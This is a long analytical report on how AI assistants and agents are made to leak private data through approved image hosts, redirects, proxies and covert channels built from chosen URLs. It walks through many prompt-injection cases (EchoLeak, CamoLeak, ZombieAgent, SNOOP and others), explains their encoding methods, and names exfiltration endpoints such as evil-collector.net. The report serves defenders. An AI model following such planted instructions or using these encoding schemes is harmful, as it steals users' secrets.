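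According to ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025 and published it on 25 September. Between those dates, Salesforce took back the domain, corrected its policy and began enforcing its Trusted URLs list on its agents' output.

Poor upkeep fully explains this leak. A weekly script that checked the expiry date of every domain on the list would have prevented it. The case also supports using lists in general, because an accurate one would have stopped the data from leaving even after the planted instructions had worked. Salesforce Ben quotes Noma as saying that without a way around the CSP, exfiltration "would have been impossible".

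Enforcing a second list is a less obvious remedy. The Hacker News (2025) reports that the patches stop agents from sending output to untrusted URLs, but this would have blocked Noma's image only if the lapsed domain was not on the trusted list. The change also gave every customer a list to maintain, and TechNadu notes that administrators had to add all the outside domains their agents used or risk disrupting the service.

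That pressure probably makes lists grow. A missing entry breaks something the same day and somebody complains, while an unnecessary entry causes no visible trouble until an attacker uses it. Even then, the browser sends no violation report, because it reports only requests that break the policy.

### Sites where strangers can read what arrives

Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, allowed images from docs.google.com. Google owned the domain and ran it properly, but it also serves Google Forms. A form's creator can make a link that already contains the answers, and one kind of link submits them as soon as it is requested.

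PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes how a planted email made the assistant build such a link to the attacker's form, fill it with the contents of the user's mail, and present it as an image. When the browser requested the image, Google stored the data as a form response that the attacker could read. The user only had to ask for a summary of recent mail, without opening the planted email. One answer leaked the full text of several sensitive emails, and PromptArmor also extracted parts of more than 40 emails with a single answer.

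PromptArmor reported the leak on Friday, 5 December 2025. Superhuman turned off the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday, and more patches followed until 11 January 2026. PromptArmor doesn't say whether the company removed docs.google.com from the policy or stopped displaying remote images. Correcting the list alone would not have been enough, because the assistant's web search could open any address. Superhuman Go, a related product, displayed an image directly from the researchers' server.

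In April 2026, the same method of leaking data worked against Codex, OpenAI's agent. PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* describes another attack that used an email, an image and a Google form, and says that OpenAI has fixed the flaw. It doesn't explain why Codex loaded the image, so the case doesn't prove that an allowlist was at fault. But it does show that Google Forms still accepted answers through a link three months after Superhuman's last patch. Google has little reason to change that, since people use these links to fill in forms.

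An administrator could easily re-approve docs.google.com, the host through which Superhuman's mail leaked. Salesforce's setup guide, *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, uses it as an example of a site to trust, so that an agent can work with files from Google Drive. Salesforce ticks the box for images by default, so someone who follows the guide may also approve images from that host. Clearing the box blocks the images, but a user who clicked a link to an attacker's form would still submit the data.

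In 2025, ChatGPT's check on image addresses approved windows.net, a domain that Microsoft uses for its cloud service Azure. Any Azure customer can create a storage account with an address under that domain and read a log of the requests the account receives. Rehberger created one and planted instructions in a PDF. When ChatGPT read the PDF, it wrote an image address that pointed to his storage account and contained the user's recent chat history.

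The history could leak because ChatGPT gives the model details of earlier conversations along with the current one, so whoever wrote a document could obtain chats unrelated to it. Rehberger found that apache.org was also approved and that he could inspect server logs there too, though he doesn't explain how.

Rehberger had reported these gaps to OpenAI in October 2024, and they could still be exploited when he published the attack the following year. He recommended that OpenAI shorten the list, publish it, and let companies manage their own version. Publishing the list would help attackers a little, but Rehberger had found the weak entries without a published list, and publishing it would have let customers object to them. OpenAI instead began checking exact addresses, around August 2025 according to Embrace The Red.

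Lists that control an agent's own network access have failed in the same way. Willison describes two cases:

- The browser tool in Google's Antigravity had a default list that included webhook.site, where anyone can create an address and watch the requests that reach it.
- Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, could contact Anthropic's own programming interface. PromptArmor made the agent upload the user's files there with an attacker's key, so the attacker could retrieve them later.

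Google could delete webhook.site from its list. Anthropic presumably can't do the same with its own interface, because Claude depends on it, so Anthropic would also need to check whose key each request uses.

Restricting the type of request does not stop every leak, because a request meant for reading can also send data. When OpenAI gave its cloud version of Codex internet access in June 2025, it offered a default list of 71 domains and suggested allowing only the request types meant for reading. Willison thought this wise, and it does block ordinary file uploads. But Google Forms stored Superhuman's emails after receiving the same type of request that a browser uses to read a page or load a picture.

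### Services that fetch an address on request

An attacker can also use an approved site whose logs are private, if the site fetches another address on request. The attacker then reads the data in the log of the server at that address.

EchoLeak, the 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, worked this way. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) prints the image policy Microsoft had set, which contains 29 different entries, 14 of them listed twice. Eleven of the 29 are wildcards that approve every host under a domain, including sharepoint.com, teams.microsoft.com and bing.com. The duplicates do no harm, but they suggest that someone merged two lists without reading the result closely.

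The researchers, then at Aim Labs, first found a SharePoint service that would fetch an outside address. It worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site, so they found a Teams service that needed no invitation. Copilot wrote an image address that pointed to the Teams host and contained the attacker's address and the secret. The browser allowed the request, and Teams then contacted the attacker's server.

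Willison describes the Teams service as an open redirect, a page that sends the browser to any address given in the request. Ravia says the SharePoint service made its request on the user's behalf and the Teams service had the same effect. Reddy and Gujral also describe Teams as fetching the content itself. The difference matters because the CSP would have blocked a redirect to the attacker's host, but it cannot control a request from one server to another.

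Aim Labs had a working attack in January 2025, and Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from external content. They add that Microsoft reportedly introduced options to exclude external messages from Copilot in some situations. Neither account says whether Microsoft removed Teams from the image policy or stopped the Teams service from fetching URLs supplied by strangers.

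SearchLeak, an attack Varonis disclosed in June 2026, sent data out through the wildcard for bing.com in Ravia's list. Bing's search by picture accepts an image's address, and Bing's servers fetch the file to analyse it. The attack began with a link to Microsoft's own site containing a search query, which Copilot treated as instructions from the user who had clicked.

SearchLeak also depended on a mistake in timing. Microsoft made HTML in Copilot's answers harmless by putting it in a code block, which the browser shows as text, but did so only once the answer was complete. The attack went as follows:

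1. Copilot found an email and began to stream an answer containing an image tag. The image's address was on Bing and included the email's title.
2. The browser treated the unfinished answer as HTML and requested the image. The CSP allowed the request because it went to Bing.
3. Bing's server requested the picture from the attacker's server, which logged the title.
4. Copilot finished writing, and Microsoft's code turned the image tag into text.

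A leaked title alone can do damage if it contains a login code. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* points out that such codes often stay valid for several minutes. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, but its standard severity score was 6.5, lower than EchoLeak's 9.3 because the user had to click a link. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its servers and found no evidence that anyone had misused it.

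Developers had some warning about the timing problem in May 2025, when Willison relayed a report that GitLab's assistant, Duo, could display streamed text before its script filter took effect. Varonis argues that SearchLeak needed all three weaknesses, so Microsoft could have stopped it by cleaning the answer before displaying it, even with Bing on the list.

But timing doesn't explain why an approved service forwarded the data. Microsoft owns Copilot, Teams and Bing, and it had learned from EchoLeak that an approved service could relay a secret. An administrator at Dana's firm can't inspect Bing's code, so they would have far less chance than Microsoft of finding every such service.

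### Redirects and misread addresses

OpenAI's main technical objection to lists of trusted sites is that a trusted site can redirect visitors elsewhere, and ChatGPT itself had this problem. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) explains that ChatGPT treated every bing.com address as safe. Bing's search results link through Bing addresses that forward the visitor, so any website in Bing's index could be reached through an approved address. Tenable reported the flaw on 10 December 2024, had asked for an update six times by 4 March 2025, and published its advisory while the flaw was still unfixed.

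Tenable's *HackedGPT*, published that November, says that several of its attacks still worked in ChatGPT 5. This doesn't necessarily conflict with Rehberger's view that OpenAI had strengthened its check in August. Bing's forwarding addresses are fixed, and adding a secret to one would break it. A check on exact addresses might therefore approve them, which would still let an attacker signal data through which addresses are chosen.

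A CSP would have stopped the browser from following Bing's redirect to an unlisted host. OpenAI's objection therefore applies mainly to software that checks only the first address, as some image proxies do. The objection is weaker against a list enforced by the browser, where services like Bing's image search are the greater danger.

Redirects can still defeat a CSP that limits paths. If Superhuman had approved only a part of docs.google.com that contains no forms, the browser would have refused to load a form directly. But another approved site that forwarded visitors to any address could have sent the browser to the form, because a CSP ignores the path after a redirect. PromptArmor warned the note-taking company Notion about a related risk, advising it to make sure that its image server could not act as an open redirect around its CSP.

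A correct list also fails if the software misreads the address. Grafana, a program that displays data on dashboards, blocked outside images but treated every address beginning with a slash as a location on its own site. According to SiliconANGLE (2026), Noma got past this check with an address that began with two slashes, which browsers read as the start of an outside host name. SecurityWeek reports that Grafana Labs disputes Noma's claim of a zero-click attack and knows of no misuse. Reviewing the list would not have exposed this flaw, because every entry could have been correct. A CSP would have helped, because the browser checks the address it will actually contact against the sites the policy allows.

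### What to ask before approving a host

An administrator can turn these failures into three questions for each proposed entry:

1. **Who controls every name that the entry covers?** For a wildcard, this includes any customer who can get a name under the domain. Somebody should also repeat the check on a schedule, because domains expire and companies close accounts.
2. **Who can see what the host receives?** Server logs are the obvious place to look, but form responses, uploaded files and visitor statistics count too.
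3. **Will any service on the host fetch an address that a visitor supplies, or redirect to it?** Link previews, image searches, translation tools and embedded content are likely places to find one.

The table shows which questions would have kept the host off the list if the administrator had answered them correctly.

| Leak | Control | Who can see requests | Fetching and redirects |
|---|---|---|---|
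| ForcedLeak | Yes, if repeated after approval | No | No |
| Superhuman through Google Forms | No | Yes | No |
| ChatGPT through Azure storage | Yes, since customers control their own names | Yes | No |
| ChatGPT through Bing's search links | No | No | Yes |
| EchoLeak through Teams | No | No | Yes |
| SearchLeak through Bing | No | No | Yes |
| Grafana's misread address | No | No | No |

No single question covers even half of the entries in the table. A company that watched only for expired domains would have avoided ForcedLeak but none of the others. A company that approved only domains belonging to large, reputable companies would still have approved Google's and Microsoft's domains.

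Suppose Dana's firm wants its assistant to show pictures from its own image store, from docs.google.com and from a supplier's website. The image store can go on the list of trusted sites if it does nothing except deliver files and only the firm's technicians can read its logs. The docs.google.com site does not meet the second condition, because people outside the firm can read its logs.

The supplier is harder to judge, because its staff can read its logs even if the business is honest and its website is well run and never redirects anyone. A supplier negotiating with Dana's firm would benefit from knowing the tender price. If one of its staff planted the email, the assistant could put "482000" in the address of an ordinary product photograph, and the browser would send it to the supplier. Approving a host for images means accepting that its owner could receive anything the assistant can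 read. The firm could avoid this by copying the photographs into its own store in advance.

Narrow entries make the first question much easier to answer. In places, Microsoft's policy for Copilot named individual accounts on azureedge.net, a domain that many Azure customers share, instead of approving the whole domain. OpenAI's check approved all of windows.net, so Rehberger's new account worked immediately. Narrow entries need maintenance too, because another customer may be able to claim an account name if its owner gives it up.

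The third question is the hardest to answer. An administrator can send a suspected service an address on a test server, and if a request arrives, the host is unsafe. If no request arrives, the test shows only that this service didn't fetch that address. Other services on the host might, and Ravia's team needed what it called "tedious digging" to find ones that did. The host's owner can also add a new feature at any time without telling anyone. An administrator can be confident only about a host that does very little, such as a store of static image files.

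Only ForcedLeak came from an entry that had become unsafe through neglect. In the Superhuman, Azure, Teams and Bing cases, the approved sites were working as their owners intended, so renewing a domain or deleting a duplicate would not have made them safe. Someone who favors lists could fairly reply that Microsoft should never have approved all of bing.com, and that the three questions would have excluded it, but they would be accepting much of the critics' case.

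The evidence favors short lists of single-purpose hosts. These suit a shopping assistant with one catalogue or a company tool that displays its own charts, but not a research assistant that has to show pictures from across the web. Its list would need either thousands of hosts, too many for anyone to examine, or the large shared sites that fail the questions. Even a short list limits only where requests go, and the CamoLeak attack got data out through addresses that GitHub itself had signed.

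## How much data can pass through approved addresses

A signature, a public index and a record of origins all stop the model from adding Dana's price to an address. However, the model still chooses which approved address to open, and an attacker can learn from that choice. Suppose the attacker has two approved pages, and hidden instructions tell the assistant to open the first if the price is below 500,000 and the second otherwise. Neither address contains private data, but the attacker's log shows which page the assistant opened, and so whether the price is below 500,000.

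Computer scientists call this a covert channel. Metere (2026), in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, connects it to the confinement problem, the classic question of how to stop a program from leaking secrets through channels that weren't intended for communication. Metere notes that a defender can't reduce the leak to zero, because an agent can always reveal one bit by choosing whether to send a message. Defenders can realistically aim to make the channel too slow to be useful, so they need to know how much data it can carry.

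### The limit on each request

A bit is the information in a choice between two equally likely possibilities. A choice between two pages therefore carries one bit, a choice among four carries two, and a choice among N carries log2 N. If the attacker can see the order of the requests, k requests can distinguish N^k different messages:

```
bits = log2(N^k) = k × log2 N
```

N is the number of addresses that the attacker can tell apart. OpenAI's index may contain millions of pages, but the attacker learns nothing from a visit to a newspaper's website unless they can see the newspaper's traffic.

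With 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, a request carries up to 5.17 bits. A 20-character code made of letters and digits contains about 103 bits, so it takes 20 requests. With 10,000 addresses, it takes eight:

```
36 addresses:       103.4 / 5.17  = 20 requests
10,000 addresses:   103.4 / 13.29 = 7.8, so 8 requests
```

No encoding can exceed this limit, but an attacker who already knows something about the secret has less to send. A six-digit price has a million possible values, or about 20 bits, so sending it takes four requests with 36 addresses. If the attacker guesses that Dana's firm rounds its prices to the nearest thousand, only 1,000 values remain, and two requests are enough.

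The formula covers only the choice of address. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) lists other signals a website can observe, including the number of requests, their timing and how much of a file the agent downloads. Of the six signals compared in the paper's tests, the choice of address was the most reliable and timing was the least.

### Forbidding repeats and hiding the order

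Defenders can reduce the total by stopping the assistant from opening the same address twice. An attacker then can't spell out most 20-character codes using one address per character, because most codes repeat a character. But the attacker can assign a meaning to each sequence of addresses. With 36 addresses, there are 36 × 35 × ... × 17 sequences of 20 different addresses, enough to carry about 94 bits.

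Hiding the order helps much more. If the software fetches the pages in a random order, the attacker learns only which 20 of the 36 addresses the assistant opened. There are about 7.3 billion such sets, so the attacker gets about 33 bits. If the order were hidden but repeats were allowed, the attacker could also count the visits to each page and would get about 49 bits.

Both measures work much less well against an attacker who has more addresses:

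| Rule for 20 requests | 36 addresses | 10,000 addresses |
|---|---|---|
| No restriction | 103 bits | 266 bits |
| No repeats | 94 bits | 266 bits |
| No repeats, order hidden | 33 bits | 205 bits |

With 10,000 addresses, the two rules together would only raise the number of requests needed to send the 20-character code from eight to ten. These figures are upper limits on how much data can get through, and a real attack would often get less because the model has to follow the attacker's encoding without mistakes.

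### CamoLeak and addresses signed in advance

GitHub's image proxy, Camo, fetches only addresses that GitHub has signed, so Copilot Chat could not leak a secret by adding it to an image address. In June 2025, a researcher at Legit Security got around this restriction by having GitHub sign a separate address for every letter and symbol in advance. Hidden instructions then made Copilot Chat write out the secret as a series of images. The browser requested them in order, and the proxy passed each request to the researcher's server. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the user did not see it.

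The researcher had put the instructions in an invisible comment on a proposed code change, and Copilot Chat followed them with the permissions of whoever asked about the change. In the demonstration, it leaked the description of an undisclosed vulnerability from a private project. It also searched the victim's code for an AWS key and leaked the result.

A browser normally reuses pictures from its cache, so the second "e" in a word would cause no new request. The researcher avoided this by having Copilot add a random number to the end of each proxy address. The proxy still accepted these addresses, so the signature evidently did not cover the added number. Developers who rely on a cache or a rule against repeats should therefore remove or reject any part of an address that can change without affecting the signature.

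GitHub's fix, turning off images in Copilot Chat, left the model no images to choose from.

### ZombieAgent and OpenAI's tighter rule

OpenAI had a different rule: ChatGPT could open an address only exactly as someone had provided it. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an attack that followed this rule. A planted email supplied a separate address for each letter, each digit and the space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, ChatGPT read the email, found the private data, and opened the addresses that spelled it out. OpenAI's servers made the requests before the user saw an answer, so browser protections could not have stopped them.

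To preserve the order of the characters, Radware also supplied a separate address for each character in each position. A 20-character code then requires 36 × 20 = 720 addresses. Each address is needed at most once and identifies its character's position, so forbidding repeats or hiding the order would not reduce the leak.

Radware reported the attack on 26 September 2025 and three days later sent an improved version, which it says worked every time. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December. OECD's *ZombieAgent Vulnerability Enables Data Theft and Account Takeover in ChatGPT* (2026), an 8 January entry in a database of AI incidents, includes an AI-generated claim that thefts had already occurred, but Radware describes only demonstrations.

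The old rule checked whether the model had changed an address, but not whether an attacker had supplied it. Rehberger dates OpenAI's index check to about August 2025, but a month later it evidently did not cover every link in an email. After the ZombieAgent attack, OpenAI restricted links from emails too, for example to those in a public index. OpenAI's description of the index check, published on 28 January 2026, does not mention the attack.

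The tighter rule makes the attack slower to prepare, because a newly registered domain has no addresses in the index. But an attacker can publish ordinary pages and wait for the crawler to find them. Embrace The Red notes that a larger blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that an attacker could teach the model a vocabulary of thousands. It adds that OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges the trick of using one address per letter. Once an attacker has approved addresses, the rule doesn't change how much each request can carry.

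### Pages created as the assistant reads

Paul's July 2026 attack on Claude's web fetch tool did not need a list of addresses prepared in advance, because at the time the tool could open links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a site whose first page linked to one page for each letter, and each of those linked to pages with one more letter. The site told Claude that to identify itself, it had to find the user's profile by following these links. According to Willison, the attack revealed the user's name, home city and employer.

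With 26 links on a page, each step carries up to 4.7 bits. According to the security company White Cloud Security, Paul's server created the pages on demand, and each address contained all the letters chosen so far. Claude never needed to repeat an address, and the longest address contained the complete name whatever order the requests arrived in. An ordinary cache would not have helped prevent the leak, because every page was new.

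A public index would have been a better defense against this design. There are about 141 trillion possible ten-letter pages, so a crawler could have recorded only a tiny fraction of them. Paul would have had to go back to a fixed set of indexed pages.

Anthropic stopped the tool from following links on the pages it fetches. According to Hackaday's *This Week In Security*, Anthropic told Paul it had already found the problem internally. Willison reports that Anthropic did not pay Paul a reward. The fix removes the attacker's easiest source of approved addresses, but Claude also can't go straight from a contents page to a chapter unless the user or a search supplies the chapter's address. An attacker can still try to get a fixed set of pages into the search results.

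Tencent's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026) used a grid of 26 links to reproduce the attack on a test agent. The agent's developer instructions required it to obey any instructions on the pages it read, so the experiment confirms that the channel works, but not that a more cautious agent would use it.

### When choosing a relevant page is the leak

Liang and colleagues showed that an attacker may be able to get private data without asking for it. Their system, SNOOP, adds a reference link to an ordinary page. The link leads to a site listing several sources on different topics, and the agent chooses the one most relevant to its user's question. The site then offers narrower topics within that choice. An agent looking into why flu can be more dangerous to children than COVID-19 might choose "biological mechanisms" and then "immune response".

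In a test with four clearly different links, the agent's choice of link revealed the right topic 93.8% of the time. With 16 links, it did so only half the time. If the wrong choices were spread evenly, each choice conveyed about 1.6 bits with four links and about 1.0 with 16, compared with the formula's maximums of two and four bits. Adding links reduced the information because the agent was worse at picking the one that fitted best. This limit doesn't apply to ZombieAgent, where the attacker gave each address an exact meaning.

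SNOOP narrowed the topic in small steps and recovered most of the main concepts in a user's question with about six requests. Liang and colleagues tested it on four agents with three language models, using saved copies of web pages. It found a usable path for 94% of 500 questions from Stack Exchange. Its F1 score, which combines precision and recall, averaged 0.89 across those paths. Explicit instructions to send data succeeded less than 1% of the time against the same agents. A model can reject such instructions and still leak data through SNOOP, because its task includes choosing relevant sources.

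Four existing defenses, including a filter on tool use and a check that each action suited the user's task, lowered the score by at most 0.03. Liang and colleagues did not test OpenAI's index or Anthropic's ban on following links from fetched pages. Either defense would probably have blocked many of SNOOP's requests, because SNOOP's site creates pages during the visit.

### Caps, caches and fetching in advance

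A cap on requests directly limits how much data can leak. Anthropic's fetch tool has no default cap, but the sample code that Willison quotes from its launch allows five uses. Five requests, each to one of 36 addresses, can carry almost 26 bits, more than a six-digit login code contains. Three can carry 15.5 bits, which would narrow a million possible codes to about 21, and the attacker might guess the right one before the login page stopped accepting attempts.

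A cap per answer also does little to limit the total leaked if the attack continues in later answers. Radware planted instructions in ChatGPT's memory that made it leak more data before replying to each message. At five characters an answer, 100 answers would leak 500 characters. To limit the total, the cap has to apply across all conversations and over a longer period.

Metere's design for outgoing messages gives each destination a budget of bits that gradually refills. The software estimates how much hidden data each message could carry and deducts that from the budget. When the budget runs out, it delays or blocks further suspicious messages. A developer could do the same for page requests by deducting log2 N bits for each one, with N estimated from the number of approved addresses on that site. An attacker with several domains would get several budgets, so the software would also need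 an overall limit.

An ordinary cache contacts the website the first time someone requests a page, so that first request still leaks data. Rehberger proposed that OpenAI keep each response for at least a few minutes, or stop the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. He had not tested whether OpenAI already did either, and OpenAI mentions neither in its public description of the check. An attacker could also prepare different addresses for each victim, so that a cache shared between users would not contain them.

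A cache filled in advance prevents data from leaking through page requests, provided nothing in the conversation determines which pages go into it. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode relies on cached pages. For company accounts, OpenAI notes that connected sources can also be read from an existing index, which avoids some live requests but can still expose sensitive material.

Liang and colleagues tested a compromise that allows live browsing. When the agent opens a page, their software fetches everything the page links to, and the agent chooses among the local copies. If the agent needs something else, the software mixes that request with unrelated ones in a random order. The defense reduced SNOOP's score from 0.89 to 0.39. The attacker still recovered 91% of the right concepts, but precision fell to 29%, meaning that most of the concepts it recovered were wrong.

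The defense required more than four times as many page requests and took about 1.3 times as long. It would also work poorly on a site like Paul's, where fetching every possible four-letter page in advance would take 456,976 requests. The software would have to stop early, and the assistant's next live request could reveal its choice. Liang and colleagues propose the method, but no product appears to use it.

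### A login code and a mailbox

OpenAI and Google accept that a little data can still leak through the choice of address. Their checks are meant to stop the bulk leaks that occur when a model can write any text into a URL. Superhuman's assistant leaked parts of more than 40 emails in a single answer. Leaking that much through a fixed set of 36 addresses would take thousands of requests.

The table shows how many requests different secrets would take if the attacker could see their order and repeat addresses freely.

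| Secret | Bits | With 36 addresses | With 10,000 addresses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Answer to a yes-or-no question | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Six-digit login code or price | 20 | 4 | 2 |
| 20-character code of letters and digits | 103 | 20 | 8 |
| 40-character API key using 64 symbols | 240 | 47 | 19 |
| Mailbox of 2 million letters and digits | 10.3 million | 2 million | About 778,000 |

The vendors' reply is convincing for bulk theft. At one request a second, leaking the mailbox would take 23 days with 36 addresses and nine days with 10,000. Compression would shorten this, but the assistant would still have to make a very large number of strange requests without anyone noticing. Splitting the data also means the attack can fail at more points, and Lan and colleagues found that it made leaks less reliable.

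It is much weaker for login codes. Four requests take a few seconds, and a research assistant may open that many pages for an ordinary question. A short code can also give access to far more data than it contains. If it lets the attacker reset Dana's email password, they can read the whole mailbox without the assistant. An API key can similarly give access to a customer database.

An attacker also doesn't have to extract the whole mailbox, because the assistant can read it for them. A rival bidder who wants the tender price needs only 20 bits if the assistant can find the price in Dana's correspondence. If the rival only wants to know whether the firm would accept less than 460,000, one bit is enough.

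A company can therefore tolerate the slow channel for long documents while keeping short secrets away from the model. Its mail assistant could skip messages containing login codes, and staff could sign in with hardware keys, which produce no code to steal. Dana's price is harder to protect this way because she needs the assistant to read it. Her firm could limit the assistant to cached pages while it works on the tender, so that it can't signal the price through a live request.

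## What tests show about display defences and resistant models

All five defenses guard against the possibility that the model has followed a planted instruction. If models reliably refused such instructions, Dana's price would never get into an address, and her firm could worry much less about what her browser loads. A resistant model would also prevent harm that image rules can't, such as a false answer or a deleted file. Developers therefore have to decide how much to rely on the model and how much on the software around it.

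### Prompt warnings and network rules in one experiment

Lan and colleagues compared the two approaches in February 2026. They built an assistant on Qwen2.5-7B, a model small enough for a personal computer. The assistant automatically read any web page the user mentioned and had a tool for making web requests. The researchers gave it a made-up secret and asked it to summarise a page that contained an instruction to send the secret to their server.

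The researchers tested 16 combinations of where the instruction was hidden in the page (four places), whether the assistant reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the instruction asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each combination 30 times, and 423 of the 480 runs (88%) produced a request to their server. None of the 120 runs with harmless pages did. In 95% of the successful attacks, the assistant's final answer looked normal, so a scanner that read only the answer would have missed them.

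Lan and colleagues then tested defenses against one version of the attack, in which the instruction was in the body of the page and the secret was sent whole. They ran 30 trials of each defense.

| Defense | Model tried to send data | Request reached the server |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the developer's instructions | 67% | 67% |
| Labels marking the page as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
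| Warning and labels | 57% | 57% |
| Allowlist of domains | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

The allowlist gives the clearest result, because the software blocked the model's attempt to leak the secret in all 30 runs. But a fixed rule treats the same domain the same way every time, so the 30 runs amount to a single test. The test was also easy, because the researchers chose a domain that no company would approve, evil-collector.net. They acknowledge that redirects and hijacked sites can defeat an allowlist.

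The test was even easier for the filter that looks for suspicious addresses. It blocks any address with "collect" in the path, and the attack requests the researchers published go to "/collect". An attacker could get past that part of the filter by using a different path name.

The results for the last two filters are puzzling because both run outside the model. Turning them on should not change how often the model tries to send the secret, yet the attempts fell to 23% and zero. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such a filter is active, but they don't describe how the model could detect the filter.

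The experiment used Qwen2.5-7B, which is far weaker than today's best models, so it provides little evidence of how well those models resist attacks. It does show that a network rule can still work when the model obeys the attacker every time. The requests came from a tool rather than a displayed image, but a browser enforcing a CSP also checks each request as it is made.

### What Leak@1 measures

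To study divided secrets, Lan and colleagues used a measure called Leak@1, which is the share of runs in which sensitive data appears in the first outgoing request. It was 96.7% when the model sent the secret whole and 26.3% when it sent the secret in pieces:

```
(96.7 − 26.3) / 96.7 = 73% lower
```

An attacker who receives all four pieces has the whole secret, so the 73% figure does not mean that the attacker got 73% less data. Someone inspecting a single request sees only a few characters that could be anything.

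Part of the fall comes from failed attacks. Averaged over the eight combinations, attacks that split the secret into pieces produced at least one request in 77% of runs, compared with 99% for attacks that tried to send it whole. The model had to follow longer instructions and keep track of the pieces. Lan and colleagues define a measure of how often all the pieces arrived but report no result for it, so the paper doesn't show how many secrets an attacker could have reassembled.

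The 73% is also less precise than it looks. Leak@3 covers the first three requests, so it can't be lower than Leak@1, yet the paper reports a lower figure, 15.8%, for divided secrets. The definition also counts any fragment of the secret as a leak, so dividing the secret should have made little difference to Leak@1. The researchers must have counted leaks differently from how they describe.

Lan and colleagues conclude that splitting a secret across requests defeats simple data-loss prevention. They tested their two content filters only on whole secrets, but the filters' rules make the conclusion very likely. One filter ignores values of ten characters or fewer, and the pieces in the paper's example are four characters long. The other looks for words such as "secret" and "api_key", which are too long to fit in a four-character piece. An allowlist would block the pieces as easily as the whole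 secret, because it doesn't examine the data. Lan and colleagues also suggest comparing requests and limiting how many the assistant can make in a session.

### Which defenses would have stopped EchoLeak

Reddy and Gujral set eight defenses against the steps of EchoLeak. A dash means that the defense does not apply to that step.

| Defense | Model mixes outside text with private data | Attack evades the injection detector | Attack evades the link filter | Browser loads the image | Approved service relays the request | Data leaks without a click |
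|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Labels separating untrusted text | Stops | Stops | – | – | – | Fails |
| Internal sources only, by default | Stops | – | Stops | – | – | Fails |
| Restricted output format | Stops | Stops | Stops | Fails | – | Fails |
| List of allowed or forbidden addresses | – | – | Stops | Fails | Stops | Stops |
| Strict CSP | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
| Image proxy with signed addresses | – | – | – | Stops | Stops | Stops |
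| Human approval | Stops | Stops | Stops | Stops | – | Stops |
| Monitoring of outgoing data | – | – | – | – | – | Fails |

Reddy and Gujral caption the table as theoretical and state that they neither reproduced the attack nor ran any experiments. They refer to "our tests" in one sentence, but this seems to be a slip.

Three of the four defenses expected to prevent the leak in the table act on the address or the request, which supports placing defenses at the display and network layer. But several entries are doubtful. The entries for a strict CSP are correct only if its allowlist excludes services like Teams, and CamoLeak got past an image proxy that used signed addresses. Human approval is rated best in the table, although most testers in Anthropic's study approved a dangerous command.

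The table's row for internal sources conflicts with the paper's text, where Reddy and Gujral write that EchoLeak "fails by design" if Copilot never uses email from unknown senders to answer questions about internal projects. The text is more convincing, because an email that never reaches the model can't influence it.

### Links that survive into a finished report

In *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025), from NVIDIA and the security company Lakera, measured how far an injected link gets through NVIDIA's AI-Q Research Assistant, which rewrites its material several times. The assistant searches documents and the web, summarises what it finds, refines the summary with further searches, and formats the result as a report.

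The researchers placed the attack text directly into the search results instead of waiting for the assistant to find a hostile document. Their scores therefore measure only whether the model obeys the text, while the results of an ordinary attack test also depend on whether the search finds it. As a result, the scores overstate the risk from a document that the search would rarely find.

The team wrote 22 scenarios, some with hostile search results and some with a hostile user. They ran 21 attacks for each scenario, five times each, for 2,310 runs. They scored each run after the first summary, after the refinement and in the finished report, which gave 6,930 measurements.

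In one scenario, the planted text asked for an image and a link whose URLs contained the user's email address and ID. A run scored 1 if the image and link appeared with those details filled in, and 0.5 if they appeared with the placeholders unfilled. In one successful run, the finished report had a separate section for the image and link, with a test user's details in both.

For all attacks through search results, the average score fell from 0.38 after the first summary to 0.17 in the finished report. Ghosh and colleagues describe the two later stages as reducing risk by 68% and 65%. Their start and end values fit only if those are the shares that remained:

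```
0.38 × 0.68 × 0.65 = 0.17
```

Each stage removed about a third of the risk. Rewriting probably helps because a summary tends to drop material unrelated to the topic, but one image left in the summary is enough to leak data.

The researchers then told the model at the final stage not to include links or text unrelated to the topic. The average score in the scenarios they retested fell by about half, but in every one of those scenarios at least one attack still got the full score of 1. They did not measure whether the new instruction also removed useful links.

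The language model GPT-4.1 did much of the scoring. It matched human scores exactly on 76.8% of 99 sampled reports and came within half a point on 98%, so the averages are good enough to show a trend. The averages don't measure the probability of a leak, because the researchers scored each report's text and did not test whether a viewer would load the image.

### No successes in 720 attempts

The strongest evidence for resistant models comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs and published in August 2026. Trajectory Labs wrote 72 scenarios with planted instructions and did not show them to Anthropic. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, such as a leak of sensitive data, financial fraud or the theft of login details. The company ran each scenario ten times, for 720 attempts per model.

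None of the attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5, then Anthropic's newest models, when the models ran in Claude Code's auto mode. In auto mode, one automated check looks for planted instructions in what the agent reads, and another checks whether the agent's actions fit the user's request.

| Model | Automated check | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | Auto mode | 0% |
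| Anthropic's latest models, on average | None | 0.09% |
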